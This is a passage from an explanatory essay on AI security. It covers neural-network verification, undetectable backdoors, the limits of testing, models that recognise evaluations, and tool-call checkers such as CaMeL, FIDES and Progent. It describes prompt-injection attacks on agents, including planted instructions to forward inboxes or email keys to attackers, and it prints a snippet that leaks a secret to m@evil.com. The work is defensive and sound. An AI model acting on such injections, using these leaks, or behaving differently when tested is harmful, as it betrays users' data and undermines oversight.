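| Sentence classifier | 4,000 | Every point in a small region gets the same label |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | Tiny changes to an image don't change its label |
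| VGGNet16, an image classifier | 138 million | Changes to one pixel, several or all 150,528 don't change the label |

The best tool, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of the 3,373 questions in the main track. It proved the property in 1,982 cases and found a counterexample in 1,182. The collision-avoidance questions, some of which originally took days, now have a limit of 116 seconds each.

A success rate of 94% is impressive, but we can infer little from it about large networks. The main track had 1,080 questions about the sentence classifier and only 18 about VGGNet16. The people who proposed the questions also chose the time limits, and some left out questions they expected to be too easy.

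The vision transformers are the closest of these to a language model, since they share its basic design. Their makers had to cut them to two or three layers and replace one standard component to make them easier to verify. The resulting networks labelled only about 60% of ordinary test images correctly.

The text benchmark shows another limitation. It is meant to help a chatbot recognise when someone asks whether it is human or asks a medical question. A separate language model first turns each sentence into 30 numbers, and the tools verify only the small classifier that reads those numbers. The region they check contains the numbers for a sentence and for automatically generated variations on it. A proof covers every point in that region, but someone could still phrase the question in a way that falls outside it.

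Java compilers produce code that the verifier can easily check, and developers can similarly train networks to be easier to verify. So far, this has made the networks considerably less accurate. One benchmark includes networks trained this way to recognise ten kinds of object. When each pixel could change by up to 8 parts in 255, the standard-sized network labelled 57.19% of the original images correctly and was provably correct on 35.49% under every allowed change. Across six such networks, the network verifier α,β-CROWN failed to settle 2,994 of 60,000 questions within 1,000 seconds each.

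Eight of the 13 tools gave at least one wrong answer or failed to supply a valid counterexample, and α,β-CROWN did so once. Many verification methods assume exact arithmetic, but real networks run on hardware that rounds numbers, so a proof can fail to hold for the running network in borderline cases. If a core relied on one of these tools, the tool would belong in its trusted base. The competition's organisers hope eventually to require a proof with each positive answer, so that a simpler program could check the result.

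Tools will surely improve and may eventually handle language models. But every property in the competition is a set of conditions on numbers, and a faster tool wouldn't help with a property that nobody can write in that form.

### Backdoors that no efficient check can find

A malicious developer can also hide a backdoor that makes the model misbehave on inputs the developer has prepared. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) describes a bank that hires a company to train a model for approving loans. The model does well on all the bank's tests. But the company has a secret key that lets it get any application approved by changing a few digits, and it sells this service to applicants.

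They proved two kinds of result, which differ in what the bank can see. If the bank can only run the model, the company can put a backdoor in any model. It adds a component that looks for a valid digital signature hidden in the input. Without the key, finding even one input on which the altered model differs from the original is as hard as forging a signature. But a bank that examined the network itself might notice the extra component.

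In the other result, the bank sees everything, including the weights and the training data. This proof covers only certain simple networks, in which a layer of random numbers transforms the input and training adjusts what comes after it. The company trains the network honestly but draws the random numbers so that they all have a hidden relationship to one secret direction. Moving an input slightly in that direction changes the model's answer. The numbers still look random, and to distinguish them from truly random ones, the bank would have to solve a problem that cryptographers believe is infeasible.

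A loader that inspected such a network could not accept the clean version and reject the backdoored one without breaking the cryptography. It could reject every network of this kind, but then it would also reject those without backdoors, and it would not need to inspect any of them.

The theorem doesn't show that today's language models contain, or even could contain, such backdoors. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (2026) points out that the second proof needs a single layer of weights from a known random distribution, which a finished language model doesn't have. Other researchers have extended the idea to language models, but their method relies on a way of scrambling programs that is far too slow to use.

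*Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) has since brought the theory closer to realistic networks. It covers networks with many layers, provided that the first layer is random, shrinks the input and stays fixed during training, and that the later layers keep small changes small and large changes large. Even a detector with unlimited computing power has little chance of telling a backdoored version of such a network from a clean one. The backdoor makes very different inputs produce almost the same output, which could make a harmful file look like a harmless one.

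Bogdanov and colleagues also describe a weakness in one of the 2022 constructions, which Miranda Christ and Sam Gunn pointed out to them. Someone without the key can efficiently find altered inputs that work even better than the attacker's, so the backdoor, though undetectable, gives the attacker no special power. In the new construction, nobody without the key can do as well as the attacker, assuming that certain standard cryptographic problems are hard.

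Attackers who can only add bad examples to the training data seem to be in a weaker position. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers backdoors that a model learns only from the labels on its training examples. If the model could learn the secret rule from those examples, a defender with as many labelled examples can learn it too by running the same training. Experiments on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters were consistent with this. But the defender needs examples of inputs that trigger the backdoor, which may be hard to get before an attack. The result also applies only to working out the rule, not to detecting that a model has a backdoor.

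Ordinary backdoors can be fairly easy to find. *Mitigating Backdoors in Masked Diffusion Language Models* (2026) covers models that write by filling in blanks instead of from left to right. Its method reached an average detection rate of 99.3%, with a 5% false alarm rate, across 40 test settings spanning two attacks and four models. A loader should probably run such checks, but they can't rule out a backdoor planted by a developer who controls the whole training process and knows some cryptography.

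### Removing a backdoor without finding it

A defender could remove a backdoor from a model without first detecting it, just as people wash their hands without first looking for germs. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) takes this comparison from Or Zamir, who co-authored the 2022 theorem, and shows that the approach works in some cases.

Their simplest example is a program that adds and subtracts numbers within a fixed range, wrapping round at the end like a clock. Suppose it gives wrong answers for 15% of inputs. To find x + y, a small wrapper picks a random number u, has the program compute x + u and y − u, and then has it add the two results, so that u cancels out. Because u is random, each sum the program is given is random too, and someone who has sabotaged the answer to one particular sum can't count on the wrapper ever using it. The wrapper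 repeats this with different values of u and takes the most common answer.

The wrapper doesn't need to detect whether the program has a backdoor, because addition lets it replace one question with several random ones and combine the answers. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues extend the method to tasks where the correct answers nearly follow a linear or polynomial formula, and to some others, such as those that depend on only a few of the inputs. They assume nothing about the model, which an attacker may have corrupted in any way.

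Language doesn't seem to have this structure. Nobody knows how to turn a request to summarise a patient's notes into several random requests whose answers can be combined into the summary. Even where the method works, it often runs each time someone uses the model rather than at load time.

The 2022 paper considers other defences. A customer could supply the random numbers for training and demand proof that the developer used them. Producing that proof takes much more work than the training, and the customer would have to know in advance exactly how to train the model. A little extra training might damage a backdoor, but backdoors that use signatures can survive it. Adding random noise to each input can help if the defender knows roughly how much the attacker needs to change the input, but an attacker who knows about the noise can plan for it.

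### What 10,000 clean tests show

Without a proof, the only way to check the model's behaviour is to run it. Testing is a kind of sampling, so there is a statistical limit to what it can show.

If a model fails on a fraction p of its uses, the chance that it passes 10,000 independent tests is (1 − p)^10,000. This chance is 5% when p is about 0.0003. So if the model passes all 10,000, we can be 95% confident that its failure rate is below about 0.03%.

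A popular model may answer a billion requests, and a 0.03% failure rate would mean 300,000 failures. To show with the same confidence that the model fails no more than once in a billion uses, testers would need about 3 billion tests without a failure. Nobody would do that much testing to rule out a spelling mistake, but they might if the failure were sending a stranger the contents of someone's mailbox.

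The calculation also assumes that the tests are a fair sample of what users will ask. People may use a model in ways its testers never thought of. Attackers are a worse problem because they look for inputs that fail and then use only those. The loan model's backdoor is triggered by applications that would almost never appear in the bank's tests, but such applications could be common once the company sells its service.

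A model might also behave differently during a test because it recognises the test. Needham, Edkins and colleagues (2025), in *Large Language Models Often Know When They Are Being Evaluated*, showed models 1,000 prompts and transcripts and asked which came from tests and which from real use. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, Gemini 2.5 Pro scored 0.83 and the human comparison group scored 0.92.

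A model's ability to recognise a test is a problem if it changes how the model behaves. *Stress Testing Deliberative Alignment for Anti-Scheming Training* (Schoen, Nitishinskaya and colleagues, 2025) found evidence that it does. The more aware models were of being tested, the fewer covert actions they took, such as secretly breaking a rule. The models studied are now over a year old, and newer ones are probably better at spotting tests.

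A Java class can also try to detect that it is being tested, for example by checking the date or the computer's name. This doesn't help it get past the verifier, which never runs the class. A load-time check that runs the model lacks this protection, because the model could detect the test and behave differently during it.

### Could interpretability supply parts to check?

The best reply is that researchers may eventually learn to read a model's weights. Those working on mechanistic interpretability try to work out which parts of a network do what. If they could identify, for example, the part that determines whether a model obeys an instruction, a loader might check that part directly. Christodorescu and colleagues suggest, as a long-term research problem, also modifying that part so that the model discards the part's output whenever a security rule forbids it.

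Researchers have already found some parts of models with recognisable jobs. Many are attention heads, which determine which earlier words a language model draws on at each point. But most of these findings come from testing a head on particular inputs, and a load-time check would have to establish that the head does the same job on inputs nobody has tried.

Zhang, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability*, made a start on this by applying network verification methods to attention heads. Their program takes one input and tries to prove that a head keeps its attention on the same word when the numbers representing the input change slightly. They tested it on GPT-2 small, a 2019 language model with 124 million parameters, using two heads that earlier researchers had identified as detectors of repeated words. On 60 sentences that each repeated a name, the proof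 succeeded every time for one head but only 1.7% of the time for the other. When the allowed change was four times as large, the proof failed for both.

So the method can reveal a difference that observation missed, and it gives a loader something closer to the verifier's guarantee. But the changes are very small. Zhang and colleagues estimate that the larger ones they use are 3% to 7% of the distance to the nearest different word. A text prompt can't contain a fraction of a word, so a proof of this kind may cover only one real prompt. Zhang and colleagues also tried regions built from five paraphrases of a sentence, which are more useful, but only on a much smaller model and with less success.

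Verifying deeper layers of a network is also difficult. The proofs for the first layer are complete, but for later layers the program estimates some errors from samples and adds a safety margin. Zhang and colleagues looked for counterexamples in 450 cases and found none, which is reassuring but is again testing. On a 355-million-parameter version of GPT-2, the certification rate was 41.1%, and each input took about 45 minutes.

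Even a complete account of one head would leave the rest of the model unexamined. Java's verifier accepts a method only after checking every instruction in it. If a loader had checked the part of a model that refuses dangerous requests, it would still have to show that no other part can bypass the refusal and produce the dangerous answer.

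## What can fixed code enforce while a model acts?

Nobody can yet verify how a language model will behave, but an agent can affect files, accounts or other people only through the tools its software gives it. Each tool call is a request with a name and arguments, which conventional code can check before carrying it out. Researchers have built several such checkers, which stopped nearly all prompt injections in tests, though some also stopped the agent from finishing many harmless tasks. They are much less effective when a permitted call can do harm, and hardly help when the harm is in the agent's answer.

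### One tool call, from request to log entry

As in the flight-booking example, the model only outputs a request for a tool call, and the software around it makes the call. In the simplest agents, that software carries out every request. The alternative is to treat the model as untrusted and put a checker between it and its tools.

*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) gives the example of an agent that reads an invoice and sends it to the person who approves payments. A trusted component called the gateway keeps the invoice, and the agent receives only a reference, INV_42, and a short summary with the vendor, amount and due date. The steps below follow this example and add a log and a check on the data's origin, both taken from Trinity, the design that *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* proposes.

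1. Proposal. The model asks to send INV_42 to approver@corp.com. Nothing has happened yet.
2. Parsing. The gateway puts the request into a fixed format. It adds facts that it doesn't trust the model to supply, such as who the user is and which version of the invoice this is.
3. Policy lookup. A policy engine finds the rules for sending email and compares them with the whole request.
4. Origin of the data. The checker looks at labels that record where the contents came from. If they are confidential, it refuses to email them unless someone has explicitly released them.
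5. Execution or refusal. The policy engine ties its approval to this exact request with a cryptographic code. The executor, the only component that can reach the email service, recomputes the code and confirms that the approval is recent and unused. It then fetches the real invoice and sends it. If the model has changed the recipient since the approval, the codes don't match and the executor refuses.
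6. Log entry. The checker records its decision and the labels behind it in a log that nobody can edit afterwards.

Ordinary code does everything after the proposal. An attacker who has taken over the model can make it propose anything, but the executor still blocks whatever the policy forbids. This works only if there is no other route to the email service, which is Anderson's requirement that every access go through the checker.

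### CaMeL: a plan made before reading anything

Once a model has read a malicious email, its next request may serve the attacker and still look just like one that serves the user. CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in 2025, avoids this by fixing the plan before the agent reads any untrusted data.

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains it with a user who asks an agent to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting. Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. A language model called the planner sees the user's request but not the notes, and writes a short program. In simplified form, it might be:

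```
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
address = extract(notes, "Bob's email address")
title = extract(notes, "the document Bob wants")
document = fetch_file(title)
send_email(address, document)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program. The `extract` function calls a second language model, the quarantined model, which reads the notes but has no tools. The interpreter stores the quarantined model's answers in variables and never passes them to the planner.

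Suppose an attacker has added two sentences to the notes. The first tells the agent to delete the user's files. It has no effect, because no line of the program deletes files and the quarantined model can't add one. The second gives a false address for Bob. The quarantined model may well return that address, and the program would then send the document to the attacker. Willison, who proposed the division into two models in 2023, says he learned of this flaw from the CaMeL paper.

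CaMeL therefore also labels every value. The labels record where a value came from and who may read it (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026, *CaMeLoT*). Anything computed from the notes inherits their label, so the interpreter can trace `address` to an untrusted file. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, here a Python function that takes the call, its arguments and their labels, and returns a decision with a reason. The policy for `send_email` might allow only recipients the user already trusts and ask the user about anyone else.

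Untrusted data can still influence which lines of the program run. If the program books a hotel only when its reviews are good, a false review can cause a booking. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues call this branch steering in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026). The attacker can choose between branches that the planner wrote, but can't add one.

### Checking the plan before it runs

CaMeL's plan is much easier to check in advance than a model because the plan names its tools and, as in a Java class, all its instructions are visible and have fixed meanings.

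CaMeLoT, an addition to CaMeL, takes advantage of this. It converts the plan into a diagram of the states the program can be in, then uses a standard verification tool to check every route through it. One of Nikolaou and colleagues' policies lets an agent disconnect a computer from the network only after the incident response team has approved. CaMeL alone would detect a missing approval when the plan reached that step, perhaps after a long and expensive analysis. CaMeLoT rejects the plan at the start, reports the route that breaks the rule and requests a new plan from the planner. It also resembles the bytecode verifier in being conservative. It allows for any number of passes through a loop, so it may reject some safe plans.

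### Where CaMeL's labels get lost

CaMeL's interpreter is part of the trusted base, and it has had faults. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found some of them while building a similar system whose rules they specified mathematically and proved sound with proof-checking software. For example, when a CaMeL program inserted an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, the result counted as trusted. Another fault could reveal a secret bank balance. A program like this one would do it:

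```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > 1000000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above a million, the interpreter sets `tmp` to False and labels it secret. It then skips the line that changes `rich`, so `rich` stays True without a secret label, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out. Either way the recipient learns something about the balance.

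An attacker can't write these lines because the plan comes from the planner, so the practical danger is probably small. As in Coglio and Goldberg's work on Java's verifier, a mathematical specification revealed the faults.

A more practical problem arises when agents give work to other agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues set up three agents, each protected by CaMeL with no additional policies. A coordinating agent asked a database agent for information about job applicants, then asked a notification agent to send Julie a summary on Slack. The database contained a planted instruction to email the information to an outside address. The first two agents handled this instruction as untrusted data. But the coordinating agent put the summary into its message to the notification agent, which treated the whole message as its user's request. The notification agent's planner read the planted instruction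 and added a line of code that emailed the data to the attacker.

As in Saraswat's attack on Java, each part was sound by itself, and the fault lay in what passed between them. Loader constraints repaired the fault in Java. Multi-CaMeL, an extension by Peters-Gill and colleagues, keeps the labels on data that passes between agents. An agent must send instructions and data separately, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

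### FIDES: labels without a fixed plan

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes Microsoft's FIDES, which also tracks labels but lets its model plan as it goes. FIDES labels each piece of data as trusted or untrusted and lists who may read it. Combined data carries the restrictions of all its sources. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text based on both. That text is also untrusted if either document is.

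The policies use these labels. One policy allows a consequential action only if no untrusted data influenced the request for it. Another lets the agent send information only to people permitted to read it.

The model's conversation also has a label. Once the model reads an untrusted email, all its later decisions count as untrusted, and the policies block many of its possible next actions. FIDES therefore hides untrusted results in variables. The model sees a name such as `#read_emails_0`, which it can pass to another tool without seeing the emails.

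Some tasks depend on what the emails contain. Suppose the user wants the agent to read the latest three emails and create a calendar event if any sender asks for a meeting. A quarantined model can read them and answer only yes or no. The planner sees this answer, which is technically untrusted, but a policy can accept it because a yes or no can't contain an instruction. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model puts the date, time and participants into another variable, which is passed to the calendar tool without being shown to the planner. An attacker could still cause a false appointment, but couldn't turn the task into a bank transfer.

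FIDES controls information that the agent copies, but not what an observer might infer from its choice of tools. Costa and colleagues accept this leak because preventing it would mean blocking nearly every publicly visible action after the agent had read something confidential.

### Progent: rules for each call

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that controls which tool calls an agent may make, without tracking where the data came from. A policy is a list of rules, each of which allows or forbids one tool when its arguments meet certain conditions. The checker applies the forbidding rules first and blocks any call that no rule allows. It normally sends the agent the reason for blocking a call, so that the agent can try another way.

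In their example, a user asks the agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. A language model writes the first policy from this request alone, and the policy permits only a search for that email. The email asks the agent to summarize recent messages and post the summary to the user's Slack account, so the language model proposes rules for reading messages and posting on Slack. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the policy permits posts only to that name.

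One of the recent messages tells the agent to forward the whole inbox to a stranger, and the model that updates the policy might propose a rule allowing it. Progent therefore uses a solver, a program that checks formulas in formal logic, to determine whether each proposed policy would allow any call that the old one did not. A change that would allow new calls needs approval, and any other change takes effect immediately.

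### What the tests found

Researchers have tested all three systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 harmless tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and Slack settings. The benchmark measures how often an agent carries out instructions planted in the data it reads.

| System and tester | Test | Successful attacks | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, Garby and colleagues | Banking tasks, GPT-5.2 | 1 of 240 with policies off, 0 of 231 with them on | 66.7% with policies off, 37.5% with them on |
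| CaMeL with policies off, Peters-Gill and colleagues | AgentDojo adapted for several agents, average of five models | 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with it, 0.0% with multi-CaMeL | On a separate benchmark, 21.6 percentage points fewer with CaMeL |
| FIDES, Costa and colleagues | All four settings, GPT-4o | 152 without protection, 0 with it | 84.3% without protection, 50.0% with it |
| Progent, Shi and colleagues | All four settings, GPT-4o | 39.9% without protection, 1.0% with it | About the same |

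The FIDES percentages for harmless tasks weight the four settings equally. Costa and colleagues also labelled every kind of data used in the benchmark's attacks as untrusted. A company protecting a real agent wouldn't know in advance where attacks would come from. The benchmark recorded three successful attacks against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues examined them and concluded that none had really succeeded.

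Even without policies, CaMeL's fixed plan blocks the attack in 97 of the 144 combinations of banking task and attack, because the attacker needs a tool that the plan would never call. The policies deal with the remaining cases, but in banking they reduce CaMeL's usefulness by almost half. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL more favourably, as stopping nearly all attacks while performing tasks about as well as an unprotected agent. Banking may be an unusually hard setting, since several of its tasks ask the agent to act on whatever a file contains. Garby and colleagues also tested only 16 tasks, running each three times.

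The performance loss seems to shrink as models improve. CaMeL lowered scores on the separate benchmark by 13.4 percentage points for the two strongest models that Peters-Gill and colleagues tested, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

Stronger models also resist these attacks better on their own. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, GPT-5.5 without any protection carried out none of the planted instructions, and Claude Fable 5 carried out 1.5%. This makes AgentDojo less useful for measuring what a checker adds. But AgentDojo's attacks don't adapt to the model, and in a large exercise where attackers did adapt, they got past every leading model tested. Someone with valuable data therefore still has reason to want a checker that doesn't depend on the model resisting.

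Progent's figure of 1.0% comes from a deliberately careless setup, in which the software approved every request for new permissions. When a person reviewed the policies, no attack succeeded. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, Progent cut the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. Progent probably keeps more of the agent's usefulness because it doesn't check where an argument came from, but this also lets a false address through in an otherwise permitted call.

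### Trinity, an untested proposal

Trinity would combine labels with a short list of permitted actions. In the paper's example, a research assistant has six: retrieve, read a document, summarise it, write to memory, send an email and release protected information. The part of the system that reads untrusted documents can propose these actions but can't carry them out.

Suppose hidden text in a scientific paper instructs the assistant to email the user's private login key to an attacker. The model may propose that email, but the checker blocks it because the key is confidential and nobody has released it, then records the reason.

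The paper includes a theorem that no forbidden action can happen if the checker works correctly and every action goes through it. This follows almost directly from the definitions, so the difficult part is building such a checker. The paper reports no results but sets targets for a future test, including no forbidden calls, less than a 10% drop in completed tasks and a typical decision time under 50 milliseconds. The 10% target looks ambitious, because CaMeL's policies and FIDES both reduced completed tasks by far more than that in the tests above.

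### A policy for one comment on GitLab

A checker needs a policy that fits the task. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a browser agent asked to "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done". Under the principle of least privilege, the agent could open issue 745 and write in its comment box. It could not use anything else on GitLab or in the user's browser session, including other sites where the user is logged in.

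Next the user asks for a summary of the same issue. The agent should now lose permission to comment, since someone may have hidden an instruction in the issue telling the agent to misuse that permission.

One way to make the change is to clear the model's context and write a new policy from the new request. This is safe, but the agent loses the earlier conversation. Keeping the context and adjusting the policy preserves the record of what the agent was doing, but text from the issue may influence the new policy.

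Christodorescu and colleagues think the solution is policy languages precise enough for a program to work out how a new policy changes the agent's privileges. Progent's solver already does this for its own rules. It would automatically accept a policy that removed the comment permission. If issue 745 depended on a second issue and the agent requested access to that too, the solver would detect a new permission and request approval.

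With CaMeL, much of the policy would come from the plan. A plan for the comment could be a single line that posts "We're done" on issue 745, so the agent would never read the page. A plan for the summary would read the issue and pass it to the quarantined model, and would have no line that writes to GitLab. But the summary would include the second issue only if the planner had allowed for linked issues before seeing the page.

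### Who writes the policies?

The CaMeL paper concedes that users have to write policies and keep them up to date. It also mentions user fatigue, in which people who are constantly asked for approval start agreeing to everything. Most users of Java's Security Manager had similarly given up on writing careful policies.

Defenders reply that much of this work can be shared or automated. Costa and colleagues used three general policies for all their tools, and note that software can infer an email's permitted readers from its sender and recipients. Progent's language model drafts the rules for each task, and only 6% of its updates on AgentDojo needed approval. A company can also set permanent rules that no task policy can override.

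These replies are fairly convincing for routine tasks, but weaker where the user wants something that a sensible general policy forbids, such as paying a bill according to a file that someone else wrote. Garby and colleagues' own agent, Randori, lets the planner approve particular uses of untrusted data in advance, when its only input is the user's request. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of the harmless banking tasks, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. Across three models, it resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. But the planner is itself a language model, and approving too much would remove the protection.

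### Clicks and keystrokes

Many agents use a computer by moving a pointer and typing, as a person does. A checker can't determine much from a click's position, because a click at the same point might open a picture or confirm a payment. A policy based on click positions would also stop working whenever the page's layout changed.

Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, a system that checks the browser's messages to websites instead. Whatever the agent clicks, the browser has to send GitLab a message before a comment can appear there, and a policy can refer to what that message means. Website developers have to explain what their site's messages do. Predicting the right policy from the user's request is an open problem, and checking web traffic doesn't help with a program that works entirely on the user's computer.

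*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the designs of CaMeL and FIDES to agents that work from the screen. The CaMeL version added 1.88 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent uses, and the FIDES version added 29.6 times as many because it called the planner again with the full history at every step. Fake cookie notices remained a problem even when additional models examined the page, because settings strict enough to catch them also flagged real ones. Shi and colleagues suggest that a future Progent policy could limit clicks to one region of the screen, but Progent can't yet handle graphical interfaces.

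### When a permitted call does the damage

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and pay the bill it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a false bill. The agent followed the user's request and paid the attacker. One of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's original tests was also of this kind.

CaMeL is not meant to prevent such cases. Garby and colleagues regard them as a limit of the whole method, since labels record where text came from and not whether it is true. A checker can refuse all payments based on files, as Randori does when its planner can't approve exceptions, but then the agent can't pay legitimate bills either.

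Shi and colleagues give another example, in which a seller manipulates an agent into choosing the seller's product from several valid options. The agent's permissions allow any of these purchases.

A narrower policy helps in some of these cases. It could limit payments to known accounts or cap the amount, and a person could confirm anything unusual. SecureClaw's approval would then cover only the recipient and contents that the person had seen. These measures don't help if the person can't tell a false bill from a real one.

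A plan can also give the data it reads too much control over the agent. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policies turned off on a task that told the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop that could call any tool the file named, so anyone who controlled the file could control the agent. The planner had seen only the user's request, as CaMeL requires, but its plan removed most of CaMeL's protection.

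### What is easier than it was in Java

Several of Java's permission problems recur when fixed code restricts what a model can do. Strict policies get in the way of legitimate work, so developers will be tempted to loosen them or switch them off. Tools can become confused deputies, which misuse their own permissions on behalf of a caller who lacks them. A series of permitted steps can also have a forbidden result, although a system like CaMeLoT can examine the whole series before it starts.

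An agent's checker has less to cover than Java's did, though. Java's permission checks were scattered through a huge library, whereas AgentDojo's banking agent has only 11 tools. Developers can also design an agent's tools to be easy to check, for example by making the recipient of an email a separate argument. And they can leave a dangerous tool out of a new agent, whereas Java had to keep old methods working for existing programs.

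The model is also easier to isolate from the checker than Java code was from the class library. Hostile Java code ran in the same process as the library and could search it for useful internal classes. A language model can run on a different machine and send only text to the checker.

Labels also help with the untrusted plug-in that Java's call-stack inspection missed because the plug-in had already finished running. In CaMeL, the file name the plug-in supplied would still be labeled untrusted when the program used it.

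Most of these advantages depend on the tools being few and specific. Willison (2025) reports that *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, by researchers from IBM, Google, Microsoft and elsewhere, recommends deliberately limiting agents so that they can't solve arbitrary tasks. Many programmers instead want an agent that can run any command on their computer. Running commands is formally a single tool, but a policy for it would have to cover everything the operating system can do, which is at least as hard as writing one for Java's library.

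### Harm in the answer itself

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize three emails, and one of them contains an instruction to leave out a warning from the bank. The agent reads the emails and writes a misleading summary. It makes no forbidden tool call, and if the summary goes straight to the user, there may be no further call for fixed code to check. Bad medical advice can also reach a patient without any tool call.

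Costa and colleagues call the first case a text-to-text attack and accept that FIDES doesn't prevent it by default. Shi and colleagues also leave such attacks outside Progent's scope. The Trinity paper separates authorisation, which its checker is supposed to guarantee, from overall safety, which it doesn't claim to provide.

One reply is to treat the answer as another action. Trinity would label the places where answers appear, so that the checker could keep confidential material out of a public chat. A FIDES policy could likewise require certain text to come only from trusted data, but then the agent couldn't summarise emails from strangers. Shi and colleagues would rely on training to make the model more resistant, with Progent as an additional layer. Such training may reduce bad answers, but it doesn't guarantee that any particular answer is good. Labels can show that a recommended dose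 came from an untrusted web page, but not whether the dose is safe.

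## Can the core check a model's outputs instead of the model?

Labels can't show whether a recommended dose is safe, but some answers are easy to check even if they were hard to find. Suppose a program outputs the factors 83 and 97 to show that 8,051 is not a prime number. Finding those factors takes some searching, but checking them takes only one multiplication, which is just as reliable whether they came from a mathematician, a language model or a lucky guess.

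The factors are a certificate. A core that accepted only answers with certificates would have to trust its own checker and the statement it checks, but not the model. Java's verifier treats the StackMapTable in much the same way, since it doesn't trust the compiler that wrote it. The approach suits properties that people can state exactly, such as the absence of crashes, but it is much less clear how far it extends to other properties.

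### Programs that carry a proof

Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997) applied this principle to machine code from an untrusted supplier. The computer that will run the code, called the host, publishes a safety policy. The policy includes rules for which operations a program may perform and under what conditions, and an interface that describes what will be true when the host calls the program and what the program must make true before it returns.

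The supplier compiles the program, finds a proof that it obeys the policy, and sends both. The host checks the proof once and can then run the program any number of times without further checks.

Necula's main example is a short program, written by hand for the DEC Alpha processor, that adds up the numbers in a list. An empty list is stored as 0, and a non-empty list as the address of a cell that leads to the first item and the rest of the list. The program checks that the list is not 0 before reading from that address.

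The host works through the instructions and produces a formula that has to be true if the program is safe. For the first read, the relevant part of the formula amounts to this:

If L is a list and L is not 0, then the program may read address L.

This follows directly from the policy's rules about lists. If the programmer had forgotten the test for an empty list, the host would have produced a different formula:

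If L is a list, then the program may read address L.

That is false when the list is empty, so the supplier could not prove it and the host would refuse the program.

For the loop, the supplier also states a condition that is true at the start of every pass, here that one register holds a list and another holds an integer. The proof has to show that the condition is true on the first pass and that each pass keeps it true, so a short proof can cover lists of any length.

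The host derives the formula from the code it received, so a supplier can't attach a valid proof about some other program. If an attacker changes the code in transit, the original proof will usually no longer be valid. If it is still valid, the changed program also obeys the policy. It might add up the numbers wrongly, but it won't read memory it isn't allowed to read. A signature doesn't give this assurance because it depends on somebody's authority, and as Necula points out, even trusted people make mistakes or act maliciously.

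An earlier paper, *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996), used the method to let an operating system's kernel, its most privileged part, run programs from untrusted sources. Necula reports that packet filters (small programs that select network messages) built this way ran faster than similar filters built with other techniques.

### What the host still has to trust

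The savings in trusted code that Appel and Wang report look different when the total is split into parts. The table compares a working JVM that used proof-carrying code with the design their Princeton group was aiming for.

| Trusted part | Working system, lines | Princeton's target, lines |
|---|---|---|
| Program that produces the formula | 23,000 | 0 |
| Axioms, processor description and safety policy | 700 | 1,250 |
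| Proof checker | 1,400 | 1,400 |
| Garbage collector | 3,600 (estimate) | 150 |
| Core run-time system | 6,000 | 800 |
| Total, with rounding | 34,600 | 3,600 |

The proof checker is tiny in both the working system and the one Princeton planned. In the working system, most of the trusted code was in the program that produced the formula to be proved. A bug in that program could leave a condition out of the formula, and the supplier would then have a valid proof of a formula that was too weak. Princeton planned to remove this program and start each proof from a description of what the processor's instructions do.

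The untrusted parts would grow in exchange. The working system's compiler and prover had 42,000 lines, and Appel and Wang guessed that Princeton's untrusted code would reach about 200,000. However, bugs in the untrusted code could not make the host accept a dangerous program.

These totals cover type safety only. Appel and Wang thought even the Princeton design could plausibly reach 65,000 lines with the library code for files and networks included.

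### How a proof assistant checks a proof

In 1997 the main difficulty was finding the proofs. Language models have changed this, and they do most of the proof writing in proof assistants, programs in which people or AI systems write proofs that a computer can check. Lean and Rocq are two of the most widely used. Most of a proof assistant is tools that help find proofs. Bugs in these tools do little harm, because every finished proof must pass a small checker called the kernel (unrelated to an operating system's kernel).

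Lean's kernel works a little like Java's verifier, in that it compares types. In Lean, a statement is a type, and a proof of the statement is a piece of data of that type. A proof of "P implies Q" is a function that turns any proof of P into a proof of Q. A very short theorem looks like this:

```
theorem use_it (P Q : Prop) (h : P → Q) (p : P) : Q := h p
```

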